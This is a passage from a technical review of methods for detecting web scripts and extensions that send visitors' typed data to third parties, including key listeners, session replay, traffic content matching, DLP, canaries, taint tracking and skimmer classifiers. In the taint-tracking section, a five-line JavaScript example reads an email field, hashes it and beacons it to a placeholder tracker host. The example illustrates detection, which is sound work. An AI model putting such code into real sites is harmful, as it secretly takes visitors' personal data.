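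The 3.18% is a lower bound because the study counted only three types of event and recognised typed data only in the encodings it searched for. It could also have included some scripts wrongly, because the researchers combined a record of listeners with a search of outgoing requests but did not follow the typed text through each script's code. A script could have had a key listener for some other purpose and obtained the text in a different way.

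### Input collected without listeners

Munir and colleagues also found 2,112 sites where third parties collected form input without relying on event listeners. They report this as 14.5% of the sample, but 2,112 is 14.1% of 15,000, so the percentage must be based on a smaller total that they do not state. Either way, this collection was more than four times as common as the interception they had set out to measure.

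Most of these scripts read the fields directly from the page. A script can use a function such as document.querySelector to find a field and then read its current text, without receiving any key press events. Listeners let a script respond as soon as the visitor types, but a script that collects only email addresses can wait and read the finished address.

The researchers traced the collection to 676 third-party domains. The most common were google.com, on 275 sites, and hsforms.com, on 268. Some of the collection had an obvious function, such as when Algolia, a search provider, took text from search fields on 170 sites, or when hsforms.com took only email addresses. Google's domains and yandex.com collected nearly all types of form input except passwords. Munir and colleagues thought this probably depended on how each site had set up the service. As with listeners, the figure includes collection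 that a site's owner wanted and some visitors would expect.

A detector that watches only key listeners raises an alarm on about four sites in ten, most of which do not appear to send the typed text anywhere. It also misses scripts that read the field directly, which is the more common way of collecting form input. Recording each read of a filled field, as Senol and colleagues did, catches those scripts but misses listeners that take each character from the keyboard event, so a detector needs to record both field reads and key listeners. Recording both still produces false alarms, because a script that checks whether an email address is complete also has to read the field.

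Marketing emails arrived at the addresses used on 50 sites, which provides a rough check on the study's coverage. Munir and colleagues had identified an intercepting script on only three of those sites. On 19 of the others, third-party scripts had installed key listeners, but the researchers did not detect them sending the address.

Munir and colleagues conclude that the addresses must have left through interception, because the crawler never submitted a form. Their own results suggest that a third-party script could instead have read the address from the field without a listener. A site's own script could also have collected the address and passed it on later, so the emails don't establish how the addresses got out.

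### Session replay and masking

*No boundaries* (Englehardt, Acar and Narayanan, 2017), the first large study of session replay services, examined seven leading ones and found them on 482 of the 50,000 most popular websites. Their scripts recorded keystrokes, mouse movements, scrolling and the full contents of each page, and sent all of this to the services' servers.

To find the recorders, the researchers placed a unique marker in each page and searched for it in data sent to third parties. When a third party received a lot of data but the search did not find the marker, they added 200 kilobytes of text to the page and checked whether the amount sent rose to match. This second test works even if the script sends the page in an unfamiliar format, but it cannot show which parts of the page the script copied.

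Recorders mask sensitive data by leaving a field out of the recording or replacing its contents with meaningless characters. Masking can be automatic, based on the type of field or on clues in the page's code, or the site's owner can mark particular items by hand. A recorder may still have access to a masked field, so an access detector can flag the recorder even if the masking works. Checking whether the masking works requires examining what the recorder sends.

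Englehardt and colleagues tested six of the services on their own pages, and also examined live websites. They found several ways in which masking failed:

- All the services left out fields of the password type, but some login forms designed for phones used ordinary text fields for passwords. On at least one website, a password typed into a registration form went to the service SessionCam even though nobody submitted the form.
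- FullStory left out card numbers if the site had labelled the field as a card number for the browser's autofill. The clothing store Bonobos had an account page on which the full card number, expiry date and security code went to FullStory letter by letter.
- Some services replaced each character with a placeholder. This hid the text but disclosed its length, including the length of a password.
- None of the services automatically masked text displayed on the page, as opposed to text typed into a field. The final page of Lenovo's checkout displayed the customer's billing, shipping and payment information, so FullStory received it.

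Manual masking also left sensitive data exposed. The pharmacy chain Walgreens had excluded many items on its website from recording. On a prescription request page, it hid the customer's name, the doctor's name and the quantity of medicine, but not the name of the drug. FullStory had already received the customer's name from an earlier page, so anyone with the recording could link the customer to the drug. To prevent this, a site's owner would have to consider what a whole visit discloses, and check again after every change to the site.

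According to Stanford CIS, Gradescope, a website for marking students' work, was sending students' names, email addresses, grades and instructors' comments to FullStory. Gradescope removed the recorder within a few hours of the researchers reporting the problem. As in the Walgreens case, the site had failed to hide displayed information from the recorder, so monitoring key presses would not have detected the leak.

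More recent studies have found that automatic masking still fails. Senol and colleagues found passwords leaking on 52 websites in a crawl where the password fields kept their normal type, so a "show password" button was not the cause. Yandex received the passwords on 50 of the sites, although its recorder had filters to exclude them. Almost all the affected sites used React, a popular framework for building web pages, while the filters worked on other sites. Testing a recorder on a single page would not have uncovered this failure.

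Munir and colleagues found that FullStory's script sent email addresses and phone numbers from form fields on about 15 of the sites in their sample, although the company's documentation describes measures to exclude sensitive information. They also identified four session replay services among the 40 domains that most often installed key listeners or otherwise stood out in their analysis. Two of the four met the criteria for interception.

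Englehardt and colleagues recommended masking every input by default and letting the site's owner unmask fields that are known to be safe. UserReplay and SessionCam came close to this in 2017, though UserReplay sent the last four digits of card numbers. Masking by default hides fields that nobody has considered, which a recorder that masks only the fields it recognises would send. Displayed text could also be masked by default, but the recording would be less useful to the site's owner because much of the page would be blank.

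For someone checking a website from outside, detecting a recorder is easier than determining what it captures. Blacklight compares the addresses of network requests with a list of patterns associated with known recorders, which Acar published with the 2017 study. A match means that the site probably uses a recorder, but does not show which fields the recorder masks. A recorder missing from the list produces no match.

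## Finding known data in outgoing traffic

Content matching means searching outgoing traffic for sensitive data, including its encoded and hashed forms. It is easiest when the searcher chose the data. A researcher who types an invented email address into a web form knows which string to look for. Since nobody else uses the address, finding it in a request is strong evidence that the request carries what the researcher typed. A company protecting its own records has a harder job because it rarely knows which record will leave or in what form.

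### Searching for a planted email address

Scripts often encode or hash an address before sending it. Anyone can reverse an encoding such as Base64, which rewrites data as letters, digits and a few symbols. A hash function turns data into a short string of fixed length, and nobody can run it backwards. But the same input always gives the same hash, so two companies that both hold an address can each hash it and discover that they share a customer. For this reason, Vlachogiannakis, Papadogiannakis and colleagues (2025), in *I Know What You Bought Last Summer*, reject the argument that sharing hashed personal data is harmless.

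A script may send the same email address in several forms at once. On the WebMD and Fox News websites, the data company TowerData collected three different hashes of the email address the crawler typed into the login form, so a search for the address itself would have found none of them.

Senol and colleagues therefore adapted a detector that Steven Englehardt and two colleagues had built to study tracking in emails. It works as follows:

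1. The crawler types an address that is unique to the website, which it makes by adding the site's domain after a plus sign. An example would be study+shop.example@mail.example, and mail sent there arrives in the ordinary inbox of study@mail.example.
2. The detector applies every hash and encoding on its list to the address. It then applies each of them to the results, and once more to the results of that. The strings from all three layers form a pool.
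3. From each outgoing request, the detector takes the web address, the body, the cookies and the referrer header, which names the page that the request came from. It splits them at separators such as "=".
4. It looks for each piece in the pool. It also decodes the piece in every way it can, looks for the result in the pool, and repeats this for up to three layers.
5. It searches the unsplit text for encoded forms of the address. Senol and colleagues added this step to catch requests that are not laid out as names and values.

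The detector can only find a hashed address by computing the same hash from the address. When a script encodes the address together with other data, the detector has to decode the result and search it for the address. For example, a script might put the address into a record with the time and the page's title, then encode the whole record in Base64. The detector cannot compute that string beforehand because it does not know what else the record contains.

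If the detector has a list of 20 transformations, one layer gives 20 strings, two layers give 20 × 20 = 400 and three give 8,000, for a total of 8,420 strings to look for. The list that Senol and colleagues published has 29 hashes and encodings, which gives 25,259 strings. A computer can handle either number easily.

Adding layers does not help the detector find a transformation that is missing from its list. A salt is extra text that a program adds to its input before hashing. If a script adds a fixed salt to the address, the resulting hash is not among the 8,420 strings. A fourth layer would add 160,000 strings but still miss the hash, because none of the 20 transformations adds the salt. If someone finds the salt in the script's code and adds the salted hash to the list as a 21st transformation, the detector finds it with a pool of only 9,723 strings. The choice of transformations therefore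 matters more than the number of layers. Senol and colleagues met this problem on the website of Udemy, which sells online courses, where the marketing company Awin received salted hashes of the address.

### The 2021 crawls

Senol and colleagues ran eight crawls in May and June 2021, so their results describe the web of five years ago. Four of the crawls covered the 100,000 most popular websites, from servers in Frankfurt and New York, with a desktop browser and a simulated mobile one. The other four returned to 7,720 sites where the researchers had detected a consent pop-up, and accepted or rejected everything. The eight crawls visited about 2.8 million pages in total.

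If a home page had no email field, the crawler followed up to ten links, starting with those that looked like sign-in or registration links. Many sites do not label their email fields as such in the page's code. A classifier that Mozilla trained to recognise email fields found 76% more of them than a search for the label would have.

In the desktop crawls, trackers received email addresses before the crawler had submitted a form or answered a consent pop-up on the 1,844 sites already mentioned, visited from the EU, and on 2,950 sites visited from the US. These were roughly 3% and 5% of the sites where the crawler could fill in an address. Nearly all the sites found from the EU were also found from the US, but some companies treated European visitors differently. TowerData, the most prominent collector in the US crawl, answered the EU crawler's requests with an error code that means "unavailable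 for legal reasons". Another tracker served European visitors a version of its script with email collection switched off.

The content match was the first step towards these figures. In the European crawl, the detector found the address in requests to some server, including the site's own, on 4,395 sites, and in requests to a third party on 2,633. Senol and colleagues then kept only the third parties that were on their tracker lists or that they judged to be trackers after examining them by hand. The manual work found 41 tracker domains that were on none of the lists and increased the European count by 13.4%. In a later study by Munir and colleagues, about 15% of the suppliers that intercepted keystrokes were missing from two widely used blocklists.

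Refusing consent had little effect. Among the sites with a consent pop-up, the European crawler found email addresses going to trackers on 202 sites when it ignored the pop-up and on 201 when it rejected everything. For the US crawler, the number fell from 228 to 199, or 13%. Accepting everything raised the European figure to 239, which suggests that some trackers waited for permission. Senol and colleagues warn that the numbers are small, since they could detect pop-ups on fewer than 8% of sites.

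The same detector searched for passwords, and found the 52 sites described earlier.

### Marketing emails as a check on the detector

A unique address also lets researchers check the detector. If marketing mail arrives at an address typed into only one website, the address must have left that site, even if the detector missed the transmission. In the six weeks after the desktop crawls, Senol and colleagues received 290 emails from 88 sites, although the crawler had never submitted a form. Most offered a discount or invited the recipient to come back.

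The detector had not caught some of the senders collecting anything, so Senol and colleagues read those companies' scripts to find out why. One script replaced each letter of the address with another using a fixed table. Others compressed the data with a method that was not on the list, or hashed the address with a salt written into the code. The researchers added the table, the salt and the compression method to their detector, which then found transmissions it would otherwise have missed.

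This check also has a large gap, because it finds only recipients that write to the address. A company that uses the address to recognise the same person on several websites has no reason to write to them. The 88 sites are therefore a small and unrepresentative sample of the sites where an address might have left undetected.

Munir and colleagues also checked for many transformations, including several kinds of compression and combinations such as compression followed by Base64, but could explain few of the marketing emails they received. They suggest that the transmissions they missed may have used salted hashes or an entirely different method.

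### Later studies

Two more recent studies planted data in forms and searched for the same data in traffic, though neither repeated the 2021 crawls exactly.

| | Senol and colleagues | Vlachogiannakis and colleagues | Munir and colleagues |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sites | The 100,000 most popular | 200 popular online shops | 15,000 sampled from the top million |
| Date | Visits in May and June 2021 | Visits in July 2024 | Published in 2025 |
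| What the researchers did | Typed an email address and a password, submitted nothing | Created an account, filled a basket, stopped before buying | Typed several kinds of data, submitted nothing |
| Forms of the data they searched for | 29 hashes and encodings, in up to three layers | Five: plain text, two hashes, two encodings | A similarly long list, with combinations |
| Result | Email address sent to trackers on 1,844 sites (EU) and 2,950 (US) | Personal data sent to third parties by 57 shops, email address by 47 | Typed data sent to third parties through key listeners on 3.18% of sites, by other means on 2,112 sites |

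Almost a quarter of the shops in the 2024 study sent the email address to a third party, whereas Senol and colleagues found addresses going to trackers on 9.4% of the shopping sites they could test from the EU in 2021. These figures don't show that shops became more likely to share addresses, because much of the gap may come from the methods. For the 2024 study, Vlachogiannakis and colleagues registered as customers, so they included transmissions made after a form was submitted. They also counted every third party, not only trackers, and chose the best-known shops in each country.

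The results show that large shops were still sending out identifiable data in 2024, and that checking for only five formats was enough to find a lot of it. Facebook received the hashed email address from 37 of the 200 shops. Shops often sent product details with it, so Facebook could link a named account to the products the person was viewing.

Vlachogiannakis and colleagues also searched for data that are less distinctive than an email address, such as a postcode and a gender. Short values can match by accident. A particular five-digit postcode appears somewhere in about one in 11,000 random 13-digit numbers, and web requests contain many long numbers, such as times in milliseconds. Searching for a postcode in a large crawl would produce many false matches unless the researchers also checked the surrounding text. Planting an invented email address largely avoids this problem because the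 address almost never matches by accident.

### Why the counts are lower bounds

All three groups of researchers acknowledge that they could have missed transmissions. A search can miss data that is encoded in an unknown way, or data that is split across several requests if it checks each request separately.

Researchers can look for transformed data without a list of transformations. If one part of a request changes whenever the crawler types a different name, and otherwise stays the same, that part probably depends on the name. Comparing visits takes more crawling and more manual work than using a list. Oleksii Starov and two colleagues compared three crawls in their 2016 study of contact forms. Senol and colleagues preferred the list partly because it needed only one crawl.

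Analysis of browser traffic cannot follow data that a website's own server passes on. In server-side tracking, the browser sends data to an address that the site's owner controls, and a server there forwards them to the tracker. If a typed email address travels this way, the detector may well find it in the request, but the recipient appears to be the site itself. Senol and colleagues excluded transmissions to a site's own domain because many of them have legitimate purposes. If the site instead takes the address from an ordinary submitted form and forwards it later, the browser's traffic contains nothing unusual.

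This arrangement is now common enough to affect measurements. *SST-Guard* (Jazlan, Gamero-Garrido and colleagues, 2026) found that 6,314 of the 150,000 most popular websites route Google Analytics, the most widely used visitor statistics service, through a server of this kind. Its detector searches requests, cookies and the page's JavaScript variables for values in Google's characteristic formats. On 223 of the sites, the details in the requests were encoded in Base64. Searching requests identified only seven of these sites, while searching cookies and variables identified 216.

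Google Analytics mainly collects identifiers and records of events, so the 6,314 sites may not be forwarding anything that visitors type. But the same server software can also pass data to Meta, TikTok and other advertising companies. Meta and Microsoft promote their own server-side services as less affected by ad blockers. If trackers keep moving to server-side collection, a crawl could find fewer transmissions each year even if the companies were receiving just as much data.

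Trackers may also collect less from a crawler they recognise, and the one Senol and colleagues used was easier to recognise because it ran from a commercial cloud provider's IP addresses. It went no further than one click from the home page, so it could miss forms deeper in a site.

One error could make the count of unauthorised transmissions too high. In a random sample of 1,000 websites, Senol and colleagues found 168 consent dialogs that visitors must answer before using the page. Their crawler may have typed into forms behind such dialogs without answering them, and recorded transmissions that a real visitor would already have accepted or refused. The published figures are therefore good lower bounds on how many sites send typed addresses to third parties before the visitor submits the form, but weaker evidence of how many do so without permission.

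### Patterns and checksums

Companies, hospitals and banks use data loss prevention (DLP) software, which inspects outgoing data for sensitive content and logs or blocks it. The software has to read the content unencrypted. Of the 1,844 sites in the European crawl, only 15 sent email addresses over an unencrypted connection, so a device that only watched the network could have read very little of the traffic. A crawler avoids this problem by recording requests inside the browser. DLP software usually runs on the employee's computer, or on a server that decrypts the organisation's traffic, inspects it and encrypts it again.

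Some sensitive data, such as a bank's account numbers, exist as a list. Detection software can hash every entry and compare the hashes with those of words in outgoing text, much like searching for a planted address. To find sensitive data that are not on a list, the software needs a description of what such data look like.

A pattern describes the form of the data. For example, the identifier of a long-term access key for Amazon's cloud services is the letters AKIA followed by 16 capital letters or digits, and very little else has that form. The secret half of the key, which a thief needs, is 40 characters with no fixed beginning. A pattern for it also matches the 40-character identifiers that Git, the standard software for keeping versions of code, gives to every change. Detection software can reduce such false alarms by requiring a mix of capital and small letters, or by looking for a word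 such as "secret" nearby.

Payment card numbers contain their own check. The last digit depends on the others through the Luhn formula, which was designed to catch typing errors. Take 5555 5555 5555 4444, a number that payment companies publish for testing:

1. Starting from the right, leave the first digit as it is, double the second, leave the third, double the fourth, and so on. If doubling gives a number above 9, subtract 9.
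2. The last four digits become 4, 8, 4 and 8, which add up to 24.
3. Of the twelve fives, six remain 5 and contribute 30. The other six double to 10, become 1 and contribute 6.
4. The total is 24 + 30 + 6 = 60. A valid number gives a multiple of ten, so this one passes.

If somebody mistypes the last digit as 5, the total is 61 and the number fails, as it would with any single wrong digit. But one in ten random numbers passes. Among a million random 16-digit numbers, about 100,000 pass, and about 10,000 of those also begin with 4, as Visa numbers do. If a shop gives its orders random 16-digit numbers, software that relies on the formula alone would raise a false alarm for roughly one order in ten.

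Patterns and checksums only detect data in readable form. They miss a Base64-encoded card number unless the software decodes it first, and they cannot detect a hashed one, because a hash cannot be decoded.

### Document fingerprints

A contract or a business plan has no characteristic format, so DLP software stores a fingerprint of the document. It divides the text into overlapping runs of words, hashes each run and keeps some or all of the hashes. The software then hashes outgoing text in the same way and counts the matches. It can therefore recognise a copied paragraph without storing the document.

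The sentence "The board approved the sale of the Leeds plant on 3 March" has 12 words and therefore eight runs of five words. Changing "sale" to "disposal" alters the five runs that contain the word and leaves the other three intact. A few such edits across a whole page still leave plenty of matches. Standard passages, such as the legal notice at the foot of every company email, produce matches between documents that have nothing else in common, so the software has to ignore those passages.

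### Canary strings

A canary string is a unique, invented piece of data that an organisation plants among its real data, and that nobody has a legitimate reason to send. It might be the record of a customer who does not exist or an access key that opens nothing. DLP software can search for the exact string, as a crawler searches for its email address. Unlike a match on a pattern, a match on a canary also identifies the file or database that the data came from. This method cannot detect data sent from files that contain no canary.

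Some canaries alert their owners automatically. The owner of a false access key can receive a warning when someone tries to use it, and a document can contact its owner's server when someone opens it. The email addresses that Senol and colleagues invented gave a similar warning when marketing mail arrived. But Raz, Putrevu and colleagues (2026), in *Safeguarding LLMs Against Misuse and AI-Driven Malware Using Steganographic Canaries*, point out that a document cannot contact the server if the thief opens it offline, or if the service that receives it removes active content, as AI services typically do when they extract the text from a file.

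Raz and colleagues therefore hid a mark in the text itself. Their system uses the organisation's secret key to compute a 16-byte identifier for each document, then embeds it where readers do not notice it. In an existing document, it encodes the identifier using variations in spacing, invisible characters and letters that look alike in different alphabets. It can also generate a false document with GPT-2, a small language model, choosing words that encode the identifier. The AI provider, or a checkpoint run by the organisation, looks for these marks in incoming text before a model processes it.

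In tests, the researchers put the marked documents through four levels of handling:

| Handling | Recovery of the mark |
|---|---|
| Copying, line breaks and other everyday changes | 100% |
| Standard cleaning of text by software | 100% |
| Deliberate removal of hidden marks | 97% for generated documents with further marks added; existing documents had reliable marks only up to the previous level |
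| Rewriting by a language model | Every type of mark failed |

False alarms are not a practical concern. With ten million valid identifiers on file, the chance that a random 16-byte string matches one is about 3 in 10³². The marks also worked in a full trial against ransomware directed by a language model, where the checkpoint blocked the documents before the ransomware had encrypted any files. However, the method fails if the AI provider does not look for marks or if the thief runs a model on his own machine.

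Combinations of marks also need testing, because adding more marks can reduce protection. When the wrong layers were added to a generated document, one mark interfered with another, and recovery after deliberate removal fell from 97% to zero.

### Rewriting by a language model

People can evade a text search by paraphrasing a document, but doing so takes them time. AI agents paraphrase as part of their normal work. When a user asks an agent to summarise a contract and send the summary to a colleague, the outgoing text contains few of the contract's sentences, even though nobody meant to hide anything.

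How paraphrasing, translation and summarising affect each technique depends on what makes the data sensitive. An access key works only if every character is correct, so a paraphrase or translation that contains a working key must reproduce it exactly, and patterns and exact searches should normally find it. The same is true of a card number and its checksum. A summary may omit the key, in which case the key has not leaked.

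Fingerprints are far more vulnerable, because they depend on word order. A model might turn the sentence about the Leeds plant into "Directors agreed on 3 March to sell the factory in Leeds". The longest run of words the two versions share is "on 3 March", so a fingerprint made of five-word runs finds no match. A German translation would keep the date and the name of the city, but no run of five words. A reader of either version still learns that the company is selling the plant. Fingerprints may work a little better on longer documents if the model quotes some passages, while a short summary is the least likely to keep five consecutive words.

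Visible canary strings fall between these cases. A translation will probably keep an invented customer's name and account number, since these usually stay the same in another language. A summary will probably drop them, because summaries omit details such as one customer among thousands, and the leak of the rest of the file would then go unnoticed. Hidden marks do worse, because a model that rewrites the text replaces the characters and word choices that carry them. The measurements by Raz and colleagues are direct evidence for this, but they cover only marks that the team designed.

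Software can also try to judge the meaning of outgoing text, for example with a classifier trained to recognise medical information. This can work even when the wording has changed. Raz and colleagues consider the approach fragile, because classifiers can miss specialist language and broad rules cause costly false alarms. Error rates matter most when these judgements decide whether an agent's tool call may go ahead.

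An organisation can rely on content matching to find keys, card numbers and account numbers that leave in readable or easily decoded form. Content matching is much less reliable for facts such as a diagnosis, a legal dispute or a plan to close a factory, because they can be phrased in many ways and anyone who learns them can do harm, whatever the wording.

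## Analysing what a script's code does with the data

Content matching examines only what leaves the browser, so a salt or an unfamiliar encoding can defeat it. Information-flow tracking, also called taint tracking, follows the data inside the browser. It labels data at the source, such as a form field, and carries the label through every computation to the sink, the point where the data leaves, which is usually a network request.

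### Following a marked value

Suppose a visitor types "Anna@Mail.example " into a form, with a stray space at the end, and a third-party script runs these five lines:

```
let typed = document.querySelector("#email").value;
let clean = typed.trim().toLowerCase();
let bytes = new TextEncoder().encode("k7" + clean);
let hash  = await crypto.subtle.digest("SHA-256", bytes);
navigator.sendBeacon("https://tracker.example/c", hash);
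```

| Line | What the script does | What the tracker does |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads the text of the email field | Marks the text as coming from that field |
| 2 | Removes the space and the capital letters | Gives the new text the same mark |
| 3 | Puts the salt "k7" in front and turns the text into 19 bytes | Marks the 17 bytes that come from the address |
| 4 | Computes a 32-byte hash | Marks all 32 bytes |
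| 5 | Sends the hash in a beacon | Finds marked data at a sink and reports it |

The tracker keeps the mark separately from the data, so hashing the data does not remove the mark. Unlike a search of outgoing traffic, the tracker therefore does not need the salt.

The tracker needs a rule for every function the script might use, to determine which parts of the output inherit the mark. For encryption, nobody can tell which output bytes depend on which input bytes, so *Arcanum* (Xie, Kasi Murali and colleagues, 2024), a tracker for browser extensions, marks the whole output if any of the input is marked.

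If a rule is missing, the tracker loses the data. Xie and colleagues found that earlier trackers followed marks only between pieces of text, or from text into objects that contained it. Such trackers would lose the address on line 3, where the text becomes bytes. *Gelato* (2020) reports that DexterJS, which adds tracking by rewriting a page's scripts, also missed real flows because its descriptions of the browser's built-in functions were incomplete.

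Rules that are too broad cause false alarms. *Privacy Implications of Emerging Web Technologies* (Chen, 2021) presents Mystique, a tracker that treats the address of the current page as sensitive. jQuery, a widely used JavaScript library, checks whether that address begins with "https:" and adds the same prefix to requests that lack one. Mystique therefore raised an alarm even when a request contained nothing private, and Chen had to write an exception for that jQuery code.

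### Leaks without copying

The flow in the five-line script is explicit because each value comes from the one before it. In an implicit flow, the script uses secret data to choose which instructions to run, and that choice reveals the data.

Suppose an insurance form asks whether the visitor smokes. A script sets a variable called group to "B", changes it to "A" if the answer is "yes", and sends the variable to another company. The request doesn't contain the text of the answer, but anyone who knows the code can work out the answer from the variable.

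To detect this, the tracker has to mark every value that the script assigns inside a branch whose condition depends on marked data. This rule still fails if the visitor answers "no", because the branch does not run and "B" gets no mark, although it discloses as much as "A" would have. Mystique combines tracking with an analysis of each function's full source code, and extends the mark to the variables that any of the branches would assign.

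One branch of this kind discloses only one bit, but a loop that tests a string character by character can reproduce all of it. Chen gives an example in which a function rebuilds a page's address this way, and argues that a tracker for privacy leaks has to follow branches.

Many trackers nevertheless ignore branches that depend on user input, because ordinary code is full of them. A form's own script may check whether an email address contains "@" and set a variable called `valid`. If the page's speed measurements include that variable, a tracker that follows branches reports a leak of the email address. The more branches a program has, the more of its values the tracker marks, and the less informative its alarms become. The tracker also has to do extra work at every branch.

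*Mystra* (2026), which presents a new tracker and surveys earlier ones, lists PanoptiChrome as a version of Chrome's engine that does follow implicit flows. Xie and colleagues also follow branches, but call them control dependencies and use "implicit flows" for other things, such as a function's return value.

### Trackers in the browser

Engineers can make a browser track what scripts do with data in two main ways. They can rewrite each script before it runs, which works with any engine but requires a separate description of every built-in function, or they can modify the engine. Foxhound, a browser with this kind of tracking, takes the second approach. *Mystra* reports that Foxhound changes how SpiderMonkey, Firefox's JavaScript engine, represents text. A mark that is part of the text can stay with it whenever a script copies or cuts it.

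An engine's taint-tracking rules for JavaScript do not cover WebAssembly, a compact binary format that browsers also run. *Taint Tracking for WebAssembly* (2018) describes a separate virtual machine that tracks taint in WebAssembly code, including a form of implicit tracking called "indirect taint".

An early study by Dongseok Jang and colleagues looked for privacy-violating data flows on popular websites. According to Munir and colleagues, it found scripts sending visitors' keyboard input and mouse clicks on a quarter of the 1,300 top sites tested, in some cases covertly through tracking libraries. Munir and colleagues found scripts sending intercepted typing to a third party's server on 3.18% of sites, but the two figures are not directly comparable because Jang's includes mouse clicks and covers only very popular sites.

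Tracking slows a browser because the engine does extra work on most operations. *TaintAssembly* (2018) describes the overhead as high, and notes that static analysis, which examines code without running it, avoids the overhead but is less precise. In the Mystique prototype, Chen switched off the part of Chrome's engine that produces fast code for frequently used functions. This made the prototype simpler to build, and speed mattered less because it was meant for checking extensions in bulk, not for everyday browsing.

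Chen's team tested 181,683 extensions in less than a month on a cluster that ran 120 threads at once. That is at most about half an hour of one thread's time per extension, or 16 seconds for each of the 110 pages the browser visited, including ordinary loading time. An extension store could spend that long on each new submission, but a visitor to an online shop would not accept a browser that took 16 seconds a page.

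Trackers also become outdated. Mystique used a 2016 version of Chromium, the open-source basis of Chrome. In August 2023, Xie and colleagues found that 59% of extensions in Chrome's store used a newer format that Mystique could not run. Chromium's engine had changed so much that Xie and colleagues built a new system instead of updating Mystique.

### Browser extensions

A browser extension is a small program that a user installs to add features to the browser. With the right permissions, it can insert its own script into the pages the user visits and read their contents. Site owners can't control which extensions their visitors install, so an extension can take data from a website even when none of the site's own scripts do. *Malicious GenAI Chrome Extensions* (2025) analyses 29 extensions that posed as generative AI tools. One was presented as an email assistant for Gmail and Outlook, had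 a five-star rating and 26 users, and took data directly from the page.

Chen and Xie's teams both used trackers to test extensions in bulk:

| | Mystique | Arcanum |
|---|---|---|
| Data that the tracker marks | Page addresses, cookies, password fields, browsing history | Also page titles, location and any part of a page that the researchers select |
| Extensions tested | 178,893 for Chrome, including several versions of some, and 2,790 for Opera | 113,099 for Chrome |
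| Test pages | 10 real pages and 100 mock ones | One page on each of seven sites, including Gmail, Facebook and PayPal |
| Extensions flagged | 3,868 (2.1%) | 3,028 (2.7%) |
| Manual check | 408 extensions: 317 correct, 36 wrong, 55 undecided | 100 extensions: 4 sent values that only a branch connected to the marked data |

Both systems count local storage as a sink, along with network requests, because an extension may save data and send it later. A flagged extension therefore does not always transmit data. In the Arcanum study, 12% of the flagged extensions only stored it.

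Chen reports that about 90% of Mystique's alarms were correct (its precision), excluding 55 extensions that nobody could classify. Precision would be 78% if all 55 were false alarms and 91% if none were. Chen found that branches caused some of the false alarms but did not check whether they caused all of them.

Arcanum's main advance is that it lets researchers mark particular parts of a page. Xie and colleagues created accounts with invented personal details, marked the text of emails, names, addresses and card information, and left colours and layout unmarked. They recorded each page and replayed it to every extension so that all received the same content.

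Most flagged extensions collected only information about the visit, such as the address of the page. However, 202 took content from inside the page, including email text in 46 cases and credit card details in 49. The tracker also found 159 extensions that encoded, encrypted or otherwise disguised the data before sending it. A search of network traffic might have decoded some of this data, but not the data sent by the 31 extensions that used the browser's encryption function.

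An alarm from either tracker shows that data moved, but not whether the user had agreed to it. A shopping extension, for example, may need a page's address to find discount codes. Xie and colleagues compared 40 randomly chosen extensions with their privacy policies and their descriptions in Chrome's store. Only 14 had a policy that listed the data collected, only eight had a description that clearly mentioned automatic collection, and none had both. DetectGPT, which had more than 10,000 users and claimed to recognise text written by AI, sent out all the marked data on all seven sites, although its policy stated that it did not collect user data.

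Neither tracker finds behaviour that doesn't happen during the test. Arcanum ran each extension for 60 seconds on each page without clicking anything, so it would miss an extension that collects data only when the user presses its button. Xie and colleagues count this as a limitation, though users are more likely to expect collection that follows a click.

The two studies tracked data only inside extensions, but the method also works on a website's scripts. Chen later used Mystique to follow cookies that third-party scripts had set under a website's own domain name. Nearly 98% of the 10,000 most popular sites had such cookies, and 4,212 of the 26,632 different cookies could be used to track people. Marks helped by connecting the script that created a cookie with the companies that received its value.

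Instead of tracking what a script does with a password, a browser can keep the script from reading it. *Passwords Are Meant to Be Secret* (Gautam, Yadav and colleagues, 2024) describes a modified version of Firefox and a password manager that fills in a false password. The browser swaps in the real one only as the request leaves, and only if it is going to the right site, so scripts and extensions that read the field get the false password. This worked on 554 of 573 popular sites with login forms. The method does not protect passwords that people type themselves, or card numbers typed at a checkout.

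### Recognising web skimmers

A classifier judges whether a whole script looks malicious, without following the data. Some classifiers search the code for patterns common in known malware. These are fast but have trouble with scripts that disguise their code or generate part of it while running. Others run the script and examine its behaviour, which takes longer and can fail if the script detects the test environment.

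*Adversarially Robust and Interpretable Magecart Malware Detection* (Pereira, Gouveia et al., 2025) uses behaviour to detect web skimmers. Magecart is a common name for attacks that plant skimmers in online shops. The data are logs of scripts running on real shopping sites, from login to checkout. The logs belong to a company, and the paper does not give their size or the number of shops.

The researchers turned each script's log into a sequence of behaviours, such as reading an input field, adding an event handler or sending data. They described each sequence with 103 numerical features, including its length, how often each behaviour occurred, and where in the sequence it first and last occurred. Other features recorded how many times the user had clicked before the script became active, and whether another script had inserted it into the page.

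Some features came from a behaviour automaton, a model made of states and the steps between them. Each behaviour in the sequence moves the automaton to another state, and riskier steps have higher weights. The result is a percentage match with known malicious patterns and a label of benign, partially malign or malign. This version can find a pattern anywhere in a sequence, whereas an earlier one could recognise it only at the start.

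In one example, a script set up callbacks (functions to run later), added event handlers, read input fields, created page elements and sent data. The automaton gave a 100% match, and the classifier estimated a 99.66% probability that the script was malicious. A language model then turned the technical results into a short explanation for a human reviewer.

Pereira and colleagues acknowledge that each of these behaviours is common in legitimate scripts. A session replay service or a search box that offers suggestions would also match the sequence, so a classifier of this kind needs many such scripts among its benign examples.

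### Scores and altered data

The researchers reduced the 103 features to the 60 most useful and compared nine machine learning methods. Recall is the share of malicious scripts that a classifier finds. The table gives results for six methods, with the last column showing recall after a program called A2PM had altered the test data to mislead the classifier:

| Method | Precision | Recall | Recall on data altered by A2PM |
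|---|---|---|---|
| Support vector machine | 95% | 96% | 6% |
| Nearest neighbours | 94% | 94% | 32% |
| Logistic regression | 93% | 90% | 14% |
| Random forest | 96% | 88% | 29% |
| Decision tree | 93% | 86% | 0% |
| Naive Bayes | 13% | 99% | 0% |

The support vector machine, which separates the two classes with a boundary as far as possible from both, had the best balance of precision and recall, as measured by its F1 score of 0.957. Pereira and colleagues chose the 60 features using the complete dataset. If that dataset included the scripts they later used for testing, the scores are somewhat too high.

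The support vector machine found four of the 63 malicious scripts when the data was altered with A2PM, but its recall was between 84% and 95% under four other ways of altering the data. Pereira and colleagues conclude that their models showed strong robustness, but their A2PM results do not support this. Every method found fewer than a third of the malicious scripts in that test, although the training data included altered examples.

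All of these tests changed the numbers that describe a script, not the script itself. Some of the altered data may describe scripts that could not exist or would no longer steal anything, which would make the tests too harsh. Criminals may also rewrite skimmers in ways the tests did not try. A better test would run rewritten but working skimmers in a browser and classify the new logs.

### Rare skimmers, new skimmers and the checkout

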